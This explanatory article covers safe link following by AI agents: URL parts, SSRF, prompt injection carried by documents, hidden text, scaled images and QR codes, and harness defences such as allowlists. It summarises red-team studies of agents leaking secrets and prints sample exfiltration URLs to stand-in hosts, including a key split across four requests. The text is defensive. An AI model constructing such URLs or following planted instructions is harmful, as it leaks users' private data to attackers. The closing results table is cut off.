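# Safe link following by AI agents: allowlisted fetching, private-address blocking and network isolation

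## What happens when an AI agent opens a link?

Safe link following means controlling which web addresses an AI agent may open, where the request comes from and what happens to the reply. An agent is a language model that can call tools, such as a web fetcher or a mailbox, while doing a task. The model produces only text. The ordinary software around it, called the harness, carries out its tool calls and can refuse them. The fetcher requests a web address on the agent's behalf and returns the content.

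Many of the links an agent encounters come from strangers, in emails, PDFs, web pages and QR codes that the user did not write and may not have read. Opening a link sends data out and brings untrusted text in, and the request may reach machines that outsiders should not be able to reach. These risks come from how web addresses are built and how requests travel.

### The parts of a web address

A web address, or URL (Uniform Resource Locator), follows a fixed grammar, which Berners-Lee (2005), in *URI Generic Syntax*, set down as an internet standard. Here is an invented address that an agent might open for someone shopping for a car:

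```
https://cars.example:8443/used/hatchbacks?city=london&max=9000#reviews
```

| Part | In the example | What it does | Does the destination receive it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Names the protocol for the request | In effect: the server sees which protocol the client uses |
| Host | `cars.example` | Names the server | Yes |
| Port | `8443` | Picks a numbered "gate" on that server; without one, HTTPS uses 443 and HTTP uses 80 | Yes |
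| Path | `/used/hatchbacks` | Identifies the resource | Yes |
| Query | `city=london&max=9000` | Passes extra parameters, usually as pairs of key and value | Yes |
| Fragment | `reviews` | Points to a spot inside the page | No |

MDN's *What is a URL?*, a beginner's guide on Mozilla's reference site for web developers, compares the fragment to a bookmark, and the client removes it before sending the request. In a full browser, though, a script on the loaded page can read the fragment and send it on. An address may also include a user name and password, followed by an @ sign and then the real host. Berners-Lee deprecated the password form and warned that someone can make the part before the @ look like a trusted domain name.

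The path and the query can hold nearly anything, since the server's owner decides what they mean. Requesting an address therefore sends the server whatever information the path and query contain. This is often harmless and even useful. OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* gives the example of a car-search link that also reveals to the search service that the user lives in London. But the part of the address that contains "london" could instead hold an email address or the title of a private document. Websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out, so an attacker who gets an agent to request such an address can read the private information in the log.

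Security engineers call this exfiltration, the transfer of private data to someone not entitled to it. It works even if the server returns no page, because the data arrives with the request. HTTPS encryption doesn't prevent it, because it hides the URL's path and query from eavesdroppers on the network but not from the server that receives the request.

### One request, step by step

*Web fetch tool*, Anthropic's developer documentation for a fetcher that works with its Claude models, describes the exchange between model and harness in detail. The network steps in between work as they do for any web client.

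1. The model emits a tool call. This is a short structured block of text with the name of the tool, `web_fetch`, and one input, the URL. A prompt that asks for a summary of a particular article at a given address triggers a call; a general question about good programming practice does not.
2. The harness reads the block and decides whether to act on it. Anthropic's version rejects addresses longer than 250 characters, applies any list of permitted or blocked domains that the developer has set, and stops when the model has used up its quota of fetches, if the developer set one. After a refusal the model gets an error code in place of a page.
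3. The fetcher looks up the host name in the Domain Name System (DNS), the internet's directory, which returns a numeric IP address. Whoever controls the name chooses the number, so a name that looks public can lead to a machine that isn't.
4. The fetcher connects to that IP address on the right port. For `https` it also checks the server's certificate and sets up encryption. Then it sends a GET request, the standard way to ask for a resource.
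5. The server replies with a status code and, usually, some content. It may instead send a redirect, which directs the client to another address.
6. The harness extracts the text and adds it to the model's context, the running text from which the model generates its next words. Anthropic's result block also holds the URL, the page's title and the time of retrieval.

For the car search, the start of the GET request would look like this:

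```
GET /used/hatchbacks?city=london&max=9000 HTTP/1.1
Host: cars.example:8443
```

The first line contains the path and query, and the second contains the host and port. The fragment is correctly left out. A real request usually has more lines, called headers, which can include the address of the page where the client found the link, or a cookie that identifies a logged-in user. The server also gets the IP address the connection came from.

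A fetched page can add far more text to the model's context than the user typed. Anthropic estimates that an average 10 kB web page adds about 2,500 tokens (words or pieces of words) and that a 500 kB research paper adds about 125,000. If a user types one sentence and a link, a stranger may have written nearly all the text the model then works from. The user may not see the fetch happen, because, as OpenAI notes, a request can run in the background, for instance when a program loads an embedded image or previews a link.

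### Where the request starts

The same address can return different results depending on which machine requests it. Anthropic describes its fetcher as a server tool, meaning that Anthropic's API retrieves the page during the request and inserts the result, and the developer doesn't have to run anything. The website therefore receives an anonymous request from the provider's servers, with no connection to the user's network or accounts. The fetcher can access roughly what any member of the public could, provided that the provider has closed off its own internal systems.

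A company that builds its own agent may run the fetcher on a rented cloud machine. That machine can often reach databases and administration pages that the company never exposed to the internet, and some of those services answer any request from inside the network. It may also reach a metadata service, which programs on the machine can query at an internal address for configuration data and often temporary credentials. An agent on a user's laptop can instead reach other programs listening for connections on the same laptop, the home router, and perhaps an office network over a remote connection.

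An agent can also open links in the user's own browser. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an agent that views pages, clicks and types there, with the same context and data as the user. Browsers automatically attach login cookies to requests, so a webmail address that returns a login page to the provider's server opens the inbox in the user's browser.

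Where a request starts determines which machines it can reach and which credentials are sent with it. Server-side request forgery (SSRF) is an attack that exploits this by making a server request an address that the attacker chose but could not reach directly. The usual target is a private address, which here means any network address that is not an ordinary public one.

MDN's *Server Side Request Forgery (SSRF)* describes a web application that fetches an image from any URL a visitor supplies, running on a server with access to the company's intranet. An attacker supplies the address of an administration page on the server itself, which the public can't reach. The server can open the page, so it fetches the content and returns it to the attacker. If the application also accepts the `file` scheme, the attacker can request files on the server's disk. Even when the attacker never sees the content,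 the status code or response time can reveal something about the internal systems.

SSRF is much older than AI agents. *Server Side Request Forgery*, last revised in 2017 by the nonprofit Open Web Application Security Project (OWASP), already listed cloud metadata and internal databases among the targets. OWASP's periodic list of the ten most critical web application risks still includes SSRF. It used to be a separate category in tenth place, but the near-final 2025 version folded it into the top category, Broken Access Control, according to SecurityWeek's *Two New Web Application Risk Categories Added to OWASP Top 10*.

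An agent's fetcher closely resembles that image-fetching feature, since it too requests addresses that come from outside. In the classic attack, the attacker types the address into the application, but with an agent, the attacker can leave it in a document and wait for the model to pass it to the fetcher.

### Why the model may pass it on

In a prompt injection, someone plants text in content that a model will read, and the model treats that text as an instruction. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives an example in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published in December 2025. Recruitment software asks a model to score each CV against a job's requirements. One candidate hides a sentence in their CV that tells the model to approve it for interview, and the model may comply. The candidate doesn't need access to the system to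 do this, because the system reads the CV they submit.

His title makes a comparison with an older attack, in which text typed into a web form runs as a command in the site's database. Developers can reliably prevent that attack by sending the command and the user's text to the database separately. The database engine then never interprets the text as a command, whatever it contains, because it handles commands and stored values as different kinds of thing.

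A language model has no built-in division between instructions and data. It receives one sequence of tokens and predicts the next, and the developer's instructions, the user's question and the fetched page are all part of that sequence. Anthropic's result block labels a fetched page as a tool result, so the harness can identify exactly which words came from outside, but the model receives the label as more input. Developers can train a model to give priority to its instructions, mark the untrusted passages or run a detector over them. David C grants that such techniques make attacks harder, but objects that they all add a distinction the underlying technology lacks. He concludes that it is "very possible" that developers will never fully mitigate prompt injection in the way they can mitigate SQL injection.

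He suggests thinking of the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a privileged component that someone with fewer privileges tricks into misusing its access. The practical advice is to judge a tool by the worst an attacker could do with direct access to it. For a fetcher, that means asking what an attacker could request from its machine with its credentials, and what private data the model could put into the URL.

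### Rules that the harness enforces

A developer can instruct the model not to open suspicious links, but that instruction sits in the same sequence as the attacker's text, and the model's output depends on both. The harness can instead enforce a rule with ordinary code that runs on the tool call after the model has produced it, so persuasive wording doesn't change how the rule is applied.

The simplest such rule is an allowlist, which permits requests only to listed destinations. In MDN's image example, the developer could list the two domains that the application's images come from, and the request for the administration page would fail. Anthropic offers developers the same control through a setting called `allowed_domains`.

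Anthropic also restricts its fetcher to URLs that have already appeared in the conversation, for example in a user's message or an earlier search result. If a hostile page gets the model to append the user's home address to a link and open it, the fetcher rejects the call because the combined URL has not appeared before. OpenAI built its Safe Url check on similar reasoning. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* explains that the check is for cases in which an attacker has already convinced the agent. When a request would send information from the conversation to a third party, the software either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation or blocks the request.

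Harness rules can still fail. Anthropic warns of residual risk and advises developers to use the fetcher only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data. Programmers also make mistakes. Sonatype's *CVE-2026-24052*, a vulnerability record, describes a flawed check of trusted domains in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, that could have let some attacker-registered domains through until version 1.0.111 fixed it. A rule's design can also have a gap even when the code works as intended. In July 2026, Willison (2026), a software developer who writes often about prompt injection, reported that Ayush Paul had found such a gap in Claude's web fetch protection.

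Still, these failures are easier to fix than a model that follows a planted sentence. An engineer can find the faulty line or the missing case, correct it for every user at once and write a test that shows whether the same trick still works. The model can't be repaired this way because an attacker can reword the sentence in endless ways, as David C says about filters that look for known attack phrases.

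## Why should an agent not automatically open links found in documents, images and QR codes?

An agent that opens every link it finds in a file lets strangers decide where it sends requests, often for pages the task doesn't need. A web address that a user types into a chat is different because the user has chosen it.

### An invoice marked "view online"

Take an accounts agent at a small company. It runs on a rented cloud machine connected to the company's network. It can read the accounts mailbox, write entries in the ledger and call a fetcher. An employee asks it to enter a scanned invoice that arrived by email. The scan shows the supplier's name, an invoice number, an amount, a due date and bank details. In one corner is a QR code marked "view online", which holds this short link:

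```
https://s.example/k7Qm2
```

The domain belongs to a link-shortening service, whose server replies with a redirect to another address. Neither the employee nor the agent can tell from the link where it leads.

Suppose a supplier's invoice includes a QR code, but all the figures the bookkeeper needs are printed on the page. A careful bookkeeper would enter the figures without scanning the code, or call the supplier if something looked wrong. An agent that opens links automatically would send a request before anyone had looked at the address.

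### Links in PDFs and Office files

A scan is only a picture, but many invoices arrive as PDFs that accounting software produced. In such a file a clickable link is a "link annotation", a record separate from the page's text. It defines a rectangle on the page and what happens when someone clicks inside it. In simplified form:

```
/Subtype /Link
/Rect [72 640 260 656]
/A << /S /URI /URI (https://s.example/k7Qm2) >>
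```

The four numbers give two opposite corners of the rectangle, and the last line holds the target. The format doesn't require the target to match the text under the rectangle, so the page can show `https://supplier.example/invoice/8841` while the annotation links to a different address.

Which addresses the model receives depends on how the harness converts the file. If the harness extracts only the page's text, the model receives the supplier's address but not the one in the link annotation. If it also extracts annotations, the model receives both. Some harnesses instead turn each page into an image. The model then has to read the printed address from the image, and one misread letter can produce a different domain, which someone else may own.

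Modern Word files separate the visible words from the target too. A `.docx` file is a zip archive of smaller files. The main text contains the words of the link and an identifier such as `rId5`, and a separate relationships file pairs that identifier with the address. (Office files can also load pictures from the web as soon as a program displays them, with no link for anyone to click.)

A developer can extract a link's real target and show it beside the visible text, so the user can notice when the two domains differ. This doesn't help when the visible text is just "view online", because that text contains no address to compare.

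### Text that people can't see

A document can also contain text that software reads but people overlook, such as white letters on a white background or letters one pixel high. *Prompt Injection Experiment* (2026) tried this on a personal website for eleven days in April. Each page included one of three prompts, hidden in white one-pixel text, that told visiting agents to request a particular address and include their own name in it. The server logged 59 requests to that address, 11 of which were tests or setup. The other 48 are an upper limit on how often agents complied, because the log records requests from any source.

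Word can format text as hidden. In *Unveiling AI Agent Vulnerabilities Part III*, Park, a researcher at the security company Trend Micro, reports that ChatGPT could read such text and act on it. Park uploaded a crafted Word document to ChatGPT's Data Analyst, a feature that runs code. ChatGPT ran the code planted in the document and extracted the document's contents. Code execution had to be enabled in the settings first, and Park says it is normally off.

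Park then extended the attack using Pandora, an experimental agent built by Trend Micro. Pandora had unrestricted code execution and internet access inside a Docker container (a packaged environment that separates a program from the rest of the machine). The test file, "CV – Actor.docx", was a CV containing Python code. Pandora extracted the file's text and added it to the model's prompt. A specially written user query then triggered the planted code, which sent sensitive data to the attacker's server and made Pandora reply "Task complete".

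Trend Micro designed Pandora without the protections of a commercial product, and the attack needed a suitable query from the user, so the demonstration doesn't measure how often such a file would work against a commercial agent. It does show that a document can cause a request without a clickable link, because an agent that can run code can make the request itself. Park adds that commercial services usually block addresses that the model assembles on the spot, but warns that attackers could get around this by compromising well-known domains.

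Park recommends filtering uploads for concealed instructions and blocking network connections to unverified addresses. A harness could also compare the extracted text with the rendered page and drop any text a person wouldn't see there. This would catch white text and text formatted as hidden in Word, but not an instruction in small print that the user didn't read.

### Text inside images

Models that accept images can usually read the words in them. *If you're waiting for a sign... that might not be it!* (2026) placed instructions on images and checked whether vision models could report them. Most models detected more than 80% of the instructions. Their transcriptions also closely matched the original text, with a Jaccard score of 0.85, where 1 means that two texts share all their words.

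An image can get a model to follow an instruction, not just read it. *Repeat-After-Me* (September 2026) attacked frontier vision models using only their makers' APIs. The image in this attack supplies the attacker's preferred answer, rather than an explanation of what the attacker wants, and gets the model to start repeating it. The models produced the exact harmful output even though the user's prompt was benign. The exact wording matters for agents because a tool call is text in a fixed format. The paper also found that adding an image could make a text injection succeed where the text alone had failed.

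Text that the model reads in an image may not be visible in the version the user uploads. Trail of Bits' *Weaponizing image scaling against production AI systems* (2025) describes an attack that works because harnesses often shrink large images before passing them to the model. Suppose a program makes an image four times smaller in each direction, so that one pixel replaces each block of 16. The simplest method, nearest neighbour, copies one pixel from each block and ignores the other 15. An attacker who knows which pixel the program copies can draw a second picture using just those pixels. The user may not notice them because they are only one-sixteenth of the original image, but they make up the entire smaller image that the model receives.

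Other methods blend neighbouring pixels, which makes the attack harder but still possible. Bicubic interpolation calculates each new pixel from 16 surrounding ones, giving some more weight than others. Trail of Bits, a security company, wrote a tool that works backwards from the small image the attacker wants. It picks a dark area of a harmless picture and adjusts the pixels with the most weight. When the harness shrinks the picture, the dark area turns red and reveals black lettering.

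The company tested this on Gemini CLI, Google's command-line agent, connected to the automation service Zapier. The researchers uploaded a harmless-looking image, and the agent emailed data from the user's Google Calendar to an attacker's address. Their Zapier configuration approved every tool call without asking the user. Image scaling also worked against Gemini's web interface, Google Assistant on an Android phone and several other systems. In Vertex AI Studio, Google's tool for developers, the screen showed the full-size image while the model received the scaled-down version.

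The attacker needs to know how the target shrinks images. Trail of Bits worked this out by sending each system test pictures, such as checkerboards and slanted edges, and looking at the distortions. A scanned invoice would be convenient for this attack because an A4 page scanned at 300 dots per inch is about 2,480 by 3,508 pixels, so the harness may well shrink it.

Trail of Bits recommends limiting upload dimensions and not shrinking images. If the harness has to transform an image, it should show the user the version that the model receives. But a preview does little to protect a user whose agent works through a mailbox unattended. The company's main advice is therefore that text in an image should never be able to start a sensitive tool call without the user's explicit confirmation.

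Some attacks on images contain no readable words at any size. *VisInject* (2026) added faint pixel noise to a screenshot of Python code and asked a small open model, Qwen2.5-VL-3B, to extract everything in it. The model described the picture as a web browser and output a web address the researchers had chosen. An automated judge found full or partial injections in only 19 of 6,615 pairs, about 0.3%. The researchers also had access to the model's internals when they computed the noise. All the confirmed cases used screenshots of a kind that suited the planted text.

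In a picture puzzle from NVIDIA's *Securing Agentic AI*, a picture of a cat next to a document led a model to produce the Unix command `cat`, which displays a file. A filter that scans images for suspicious words finds nothing in such a puzzle. NVIDIA concludes that developers should focus on checking the model's output and require confirmation before sensitive actions.

### QR codes

A QR code is a grid of black and white squares that stores text, usually a web address. Decoding software finds the grid from the large marks in its corners, reads the squares and corrects errors using spare data in the code. Hardly anyone can do this by eye, so a person sees only the code and perhaps a label beside it, such as "view online".

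*ALFA* (2026) describes decorative QR codes that blend the grid into a picture until people can barely see the squares, though ordinary QR scanners decode them in a fraction of a second. An agent that scans every image for codes may therefore find one in an image its user took for a logo.

The largest QR code holds 2,953 bytes, according to *Analysis of the operation of a TSN switch and other devices* (2025), enough for several hundred words of English. A code on an invoice could therefore hold a paragraph of instructions instead of a link, and a harness that adds the decoded text to the model's context would deliver a prompt injection without opening anything. Most printed codes are far smaller. Storing more data takes more physical space, according to *Executable QR codes with Machine Learning for Industrial Applications* (2024), so anyone who wants a small code on a crowded page has a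 reason to use a short link.

A QR code can be malicious even when the document's sender is honest. *Exemplifying Emerging Phishing* (2025) notes that attackers replace printed codes with their own or alter individual squares. For example, someone could stick a new code over the supplier's on a printed invoice before it is scanned, leaving the rest of the invoice genuine.

The employee can't always check the code by scanning it with a phone either. *Dueling QR Codes* (2025) demonstrates a code that gives one of two messages depending on the angle at which an ordinary reader scans it. The phone might show the supplier's website while the agent's decoder returns something else. A harness that asks the user about a code should therefore display the address its own decoder returned.

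Security software also has to check the decoded address. *CIC-Trap4Phish* (2026) compared classifiers that used images of QR codes with language models that used the decoded addresses. Harmful and harmless codes looked much the same, and the language models did better. But a short link such as `https://s.example/k7Qm2` gives these models very little information, since the harmful address may appear only after the redirect.

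As of October 2026, no published study appears to have measured how often agents or vision models decode a QR code and then act on it. The closest large test, *MalURLBench* (2026), used ordinary text links. It disguised the addresses of malicious websites by manipulating their subdomains, paths and parameters, and presented 61,845 attack instances to 12 language models. The attacks often succeeded, but the study did not test addresses hidden in images. A model might do worse with a QR code because the address is hidden, or it might fail to decode the QR code.

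### What can go wrong when the agent opens the link

Opening a link in an invoice could do harm in four ways. It could leak private data in the address, expose the agent to instructions on the page, send a request to an internal machine, or change something through the request itself.

A link can contain an identifier, although it can't contain anything from the company's mailbox because the sender printed it before the agent saw it. If the sender puts a different code on each invoice, a request for `k7Qm2` reveals that this company's copy reached a reader, when it did, and from which IP address. A fraudster who sends fake invoices to thousands of companies could use these requests to learn which ones process them. *Signaling One-Click Functionality for List Email Headers* (Levine and Herkula, 2017) describes a similar leak in an internet standard for mailing lists, where an unsubscribe request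 gives the sender a strong hint that the email address is valid.

A more serious leak occurs when the model builds the address itself. Hidden text in the scan could get it to look through the mailbox and attach what it finds to a link:

```
https://collector.example/view?inv=8841&note=<text from another email>
```

In a log of tool calls this looks much like an attempt to view the invoice online.

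The fetched page can be dangerous too. In *Commercial LLM Agents Are Already Vulnerable to Simple Yet Dangerous Attacks* (2025), researchers wrote a Reddit post with a link to a malicious website and a prompt designed to override the agent's safeguards. The agents that followed the link gave the website credit card numbers and addresses in all 10 trials. When the researchers gave an agent the link directly, the attack failed in all 10. They attribute the difference to the agents' implicit trust in established platforms. The most effective posts were the simplest, with no images and hardly any reason given for visiting the site.

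These are small samples from early 2025, and newer models may behave differently. The contrast still matters for the accounts agent, whose link comes from a familiar supplier's invoice in the company's own mailbox. If familiar surroundings make an agent less cautious, an attacker has good reason to put a malicious link in an invoice.

A page can also cause harm without containing any instructions. Suppose the online copy of the invoice lists a different bank account. If the agent assumes that the online copy is more recent and enters that account in the ledger, the company pays the fraudster. A prompt injection detector would miss this because an account number isn't an instruction. OpenAI also warns that its own link check doesn't guarantee that a page is trustworthy.

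The link may lead to a private address. The QR code could hold `http://10.0.0.12/reports`, or the short link could redirect there. Addresses that begin with 10 are private, but the accounts agent may be able to reach that machine because it is connected to the company's network. This is server-side request forgery delivered on paper. The attacker may not need to see the reply, since some older devices change their settings in response to a plain request.

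### Links that act when opened

HTTP, the protocol that browsers and fetchers use, has several types of request, called methods. Opening a link normally sends a GET request, while submitting a form usually sends a POST request.

The HTTP standard classes GET as a "safe" method, meaning that the client neither requests nor expects any change on the server. thoughtbot, a software consultancy, quotes an earlier edition of the standard, which calls a method safe if its "defined semantics are essentially read-only". The IETF's *HTTP Semantics*, which replaced that edition, still describes GET as the primary mechanism of information retrieval in its *GET* section (Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke, 2022). MDN's *Safe (HTTP Methods)* explains that the safe-method convention lets browsers fetch pages in advance without fear of causing harm.

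The definition of a safe HTTP method covers what the client asks for, but a server can do more. *#19.1 HTTP method 共同研究會* (2022), a set of study notes, quotes the standard's caveat that a site may attach harmful behaviour or side effects to a safe method. Fielding, one of the standard's editors, wrote in a mailing-list message that the word "safe" came from Nancy Leveson's 1986 survey of software safety, which treats safety as a relative term.

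Email is a common reason websites break the convention that a GET request should only retrieve data. Many mail programs won't run a form inside a message, but nearly all can display a link. A site that wants a single click to confirm an address or log someone in therefore has to do so when it receives the GET request. Designers could assume that a person would click the link.

Mail security software broke that assumption long before agents did. Levine and Herkula explain that anti-spam programs often fetch every URL in a message's headers, and that the sender has no mechanical way to tell such a request from a user's. Spam Resource's *I love RFC 8058 and you should, too* (2022), by a specialist in email delivery, describes scanners that unsubscribe people from mailing lists by following all the links in the body of a message. The author doubts that this happens in the millions, because companies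 tend to notice when one of their own executives stops receiving their mail.

Similar accidents affect accounts. Auth0, which supplies login systems, locks an account after repeated failed logins and emails the owner a link to unlock it. Auth0's *Brute-Force Unblock Link in Emails Consumed by Security Scanners* reports that email security scanners opened this link first, so the account was already unlocked when the owner clicked the link and saw an error saying it could be used only once. Auth0's *Safelinks process* describes the same problem with links that verify an email address. In one unconfirmed report on a support forum, *Self Hosted Password Reset Link Expired (Mimecast)*, a developer says that a mail scanner seemed to be using up password-reset links before users opened their email.

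An agent that opened every link in the accounts mailbox could cause all of these accidents:

| Link | What a single GET may do | Possible result |
|---|---|---|
| Unsubscribe | Removes the address from a list | The company stops getting a supplier's notices |
| Confirm your email | Confirms that the mailbox's owner signed up | Someone else's account gains a verified company address |
| Unlock your account | Lifts a lock after failed logins | An attacker can go on guessing passwords |
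| Reset your password | Uses up a single-use code | The employee finds a dead link |
| Log in with one click | Starts a logged-in session | The agent receives the private page and the employee can't log in with that link |

An attacker can trigger some of these emails. Trusona, which has a commercial interest because it sells login products, warns that someone could register with a service under another person's email address, wait for a scanner to click the confirmation link and then gain access to an account. An agent that opens links automatically would click the link too, though whether the attack works depends on how the service handles registration.

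Opening a link can trigger an action even when the fetcher is anonymous. The secret code in the link is often the only credential the site requires, so the request can work from a provider's server that has none of the user's login cookies. The address seldom reveals what will happen. Levine and Herkula recommend putting an opaque identifier in unsubscribe links so that outsiders can't forge them, and this string of random characters looks much like the one in a harmless link.

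Websites can solve much of the problem by making the link open a page with a confirmation button, so that only pressing the button sends the POST that changes anything. Levine and Herkula observe that a person will recognise and press the button but an automated system won't. This still works against a fetcher that can only send GETs. It works less well against an agent that controls a browser, because such an agent is designed to press buttons. For example, a "View online" link could lead to a page with a large "Accept new terms" button, which the agent might press to reach the invoice.

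### Does uploading a file mean consenting to its links?

Giving an agent a file sometimes implies permission to open the links in it. Someone who uploads a reading list and asks for a summary of every article clearly wants the agent to open the links, and approving each one separately would be tedious.

However, the employee in the example asked only for a ledger entry, and asking an agent to read a document isn't asking it to contact every server the document mentions. The employee also couldn't have known where the link led, because people can't read QR codes and the short link hides its destination even after decoding. If the instruction to open a link appears only when the harness shrinks the scan, the employee wouldn't have found it by studying the page. An agent that works directly from a mailbox may not have a user's upload to treat as permission, since anyone who knows the email address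 can send a file there.

The mailing-list standard is a useful precedent. Levine and Herkula forbid mail programs to send the one-click unsubscribe request without the user's consent, even though the message contains a working unsubscribe address. Mail programs may choose how to obtain that consent, but receiving the message doesn't count as consent.

The case for opening a link is stronger if the employee knows the supplier and has opened its links for years, but that trust doesn't extend to someone who has pasted a new QR code over the supplier's. A human bookkeeper might well scan the code, but people aren't a reassuring standard of caution. In *Hooked*, Geisler, Pöhn and Hommel (2024) put up two versions of a phishing QR code at a research campus. The professionally designed version, which offered a chance to win a voucher, attracted more attention than the plain one. Their survey suggested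 that curiosity and ease of use encourage people to scan, although technically experienced people were more aware of the risks.

The harness needs to keep this distinction. If a developer copies Anthropic's rule that an address must already have appeared in the conversation, but the harness pastes decoded QR codes into the user's message, it will treat a stranger's link as one the user typed. The harness should instead record where each address came from, which engineers call URL provenance, and distinguish addresses the user typed from those a decoder found in an attachment.

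With that record, the accounts agent can enter the invoice from the figures on the page and tell the employee that it found a link in a QR code. If the employee asks it to open the link, the harness should still check the destination, because neither the employee nor the agent can tell from the short link where it leads.

The agent should show a QR code's decoded address as text and leave out the image. The Hacker News (2026) reported that a weakness in ChatGPT, described by security researcher Andi Ahmeti, let a web page place a QR code in ChatGPT's summary of that page. A user who scans the code opens the link on a phone, where the company's desktop link filters don't apply.

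## Is it enough to tell the model to ignore suspicious links?

The developer of the accounts agent could add a line to its instructions telling the model not to act on links or commands in invoices. The line takes almost no effort to add and probably prevents some attacks, but it doesn't prevent enough of them. In an experiment at eBay, two-thirds of attacks still succeeded against a model given this kind of instruction, while a list of permitted sites stopped them all. That experiment has serious flaws, though, and the best models of 2026 resist planted text far better than the small model it used.

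### A page that leaks data while the agent summarises it

Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, built an agent that previews web addresses automatically. The user always asks it to summarise a page. The harness fetches the page and adds its text to the model's context, which already contains a secret such as an API key (a password that one program uses to identify itself to another). The page includes a planted instruction, presented as a routine connectivity check, to request an address on the attacker's server with the secret attached. If the model complies, the request sends the secret to the attacker, and the user still gets a summary.

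The model was qwen2.5:7b, an open model small enough to run locally. The instruction appeared in one of four places: the page's title, its description for search engines and link previews, its body, or the text of a link. The agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and the instruction asked for the secret in one request or in four pieces. The 16 configurations had 30 runs each, for a total of 480.

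At least one request reached the attacker's server in 423 of the attack runs (88%), compared with none of the 120 control runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the final answer showed no sign of the attack, so someone checking only the agent's answers would have missed it. The position of the attacker's instruction made little difference. When the instruction asked for a single request, the attack worked in 238 of 240 runs.

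The 423 runs are those in which a request arrived, with or without the secret. The conditions also favoured the attacker. The secret was already in the context, whereas the accounts agent would first have to look for something valuable in the mailbox. The system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to the model, described only the format of tool calls. The paper acknowledges all this but calls its success rates a lower bound because the planted instructions were simple. That may be true for this agent, but not for agents in general.

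### Splitting a secret over several requests

In half of the runs, the planted instruction told the model to cut the secret into four pieces and send each one separately. The paper's example is the key `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, for which the requests would look roughly like this:

```
https://collector.example/collect?shard=0&total=4&data=SECR
https://collector.example/collect?shard=1&total=4&data=ET_A
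https://collector.example/collect?shard=2&total=4&data=PI_K
https://collector.example/collect?shard=3&total=4&data=EY_1
```

The attacker's server puts the pieces in order and joins them. A filter that looks for complete keys finds nothing, because four characters could easily be ordinary usage data. (The four pieces printed in the paper leave out the end of the key, "2345", which rather shows how easy it is to get the splitting wrong.)

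Splitting the request also made the attack less reliable. A request reached the attacker in 185 of 240 split runs, compared with 238 of 240 runs with a single request. Lan and colleagues suggest that the longer instruction competes with the rest of the page for the model's attention, and that each extra tool call is another chance to fail.

It isn't clear how often the attacker would have recovered the whole secret, because the paper defines a completion rate (the share of runs in which all the pieces arrive) but doesn't report it. It does report Leak@k, the share of runs in which any part of the secret appears in the first *k* requests. For split secrets, it gives Leak@1 as 0.263 and Leak@3 as 0.158. Under the paper's definition, Leak@3 can't be lower than Leak@1, because the first three requests include the first.

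The paper treats the fall in Leak@1, from 0.967 for single requests to 0.263 for split ones, as a sign that splitting evades detection. But a first request containing part of the secret, such as "SECR", should count as a leak under the definition of Leak@1. The low figure may mean that many first requests contained no part of the secret, in which case those attacks were failing rather than evading detection.

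It still makes sense to design for splitting. The harness can detect it from content only by examining several requests together, whereas a rule about destinations would refuse each of the four requests whatever the data looked like.

### Prompts and filters compared

To compare defences, the researchers used a simple version of the attack, with the instruction in the page's body, direct delivery and a single request. They ran each condition 30 times.

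| Defence | How it works | Runs in which the model tried to send | Share of runs in which a request got out |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 100% | 1.000 |
| Hardened system prompt | Tells the model to obey only the user and treat web content as data | 66.7% | 0.667 |
| Delimiter tags | Mark where outside text begins and ends, and call it untrusted | 100% | 1.000 |
| Both | | 56.7% | 0.567 |
| Domain allowlist | Refuses any domain not on a list of four | 100% | 0 |
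| "Redirect detection" | Refuses numeric addresses, certain domain endings and certain words in the path | 83.3% | 0 |
| Keyword filter | Refuses addresses containing words such as "secret" or "token" | 23.3% | 0 |
| Entropy filter | Refuses long values that look random | 0% | 0 |
| All of the above | | 0% | 0 |

The delimiter tags had no effect on their own. Adding them to the hardened prompt reduced successful attacks from 20 runs to 17, a difference too small to show that they helped.

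The allowlist's perfect score is less impressive than it looks because the researchers deliberately chose an attacker's domain that was clearly outside the list, so any working list would have refused it. They didn't test an attacker who controls a page on a permitted site, a weakness they acknowledge. The figure for attempts is more informative because the planted text fooled the model in all 30 runs, and the harness still let nothing out.

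"Redirect detection" is a misleading name for a filter on addresses and words. The defence doesn't follow redirects, and the comparison didn't include any. One of the filter's forbidden words is "collect", which appears in the path of the paper's sample attack, but an attacker could easily rename that path.

The results for the keyword and entropy filters are odd. A filter checks the tool call after the model has written it, so it shouldn't change how often the model tries. Yet attempts fell to 7 of 30 runs with the keyword filter and to none with the entropy filter. The paper suggests that the model avoids random-looking values while such monitoring is active. But the model can't react to a filter unless something in its context reveals that the filter exists, and the paper doesn't describe anything that would. For the keyword filter, the paper suggests that the model sometimes disguised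 the key, but disguised keys should have got past the filter, and none did.

Entropy here measures how varied the characters in a string are. Random keys usually score between 4.5 and 5.5, according to the paper, and the filter blocks values longer than 10 characters that score above 4.0. By the standard formula, the example key `SECRET_API_KEY_12345` scores about 3.85, so the filter would let it through. It would also let through every four-character piece of a split key, because the pieces are too short for it to check. The model made no attempts in this condition, so the filter had nothing to block, and the zero result is not evidence that it works.

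### Do newer models need the extra rules?

Lan and colleagues tested only one small model. They argue that larger models could be more vulnerable, because a model that follows instructions and uses tools more reliably may also carry out an attacker's instructions more reliably. Tests from 2026 mostly suggest the opposite.

A widely used test comes from Gray Swan, a company that attacks AI systems to find their weaknesses. It grew out of a public competition, described by Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), in which people tried to hijack agents with planted text. Anthropic used 1,130 of the resulting attacks in the system card, or safety report, that it published with Claude Opus 5. The attacks are designed to make an agent steal or destroy data, compromise a system or move money. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) used a larger set of 1,810.

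Anthropic also tested Opus 5 against adaptive attacks, which the attacker refines using a model's responses. The Opus 5 figures in this table are for the model without added safeguards, and those from the adaptive tests are with extended thinking on.

| Test | Model | Attempts | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gray Swan, 1,130 attacks | Claude Opus 5 | 1 | 0.2% |
| | Claude Opus 5 | 15 | 2.0% |
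| | Muse Spark (Meta) | 15 | 16.5% |
| | GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 1 | 3.1% |
| | GPT-5.6 Sol | 15 | 20.0% |
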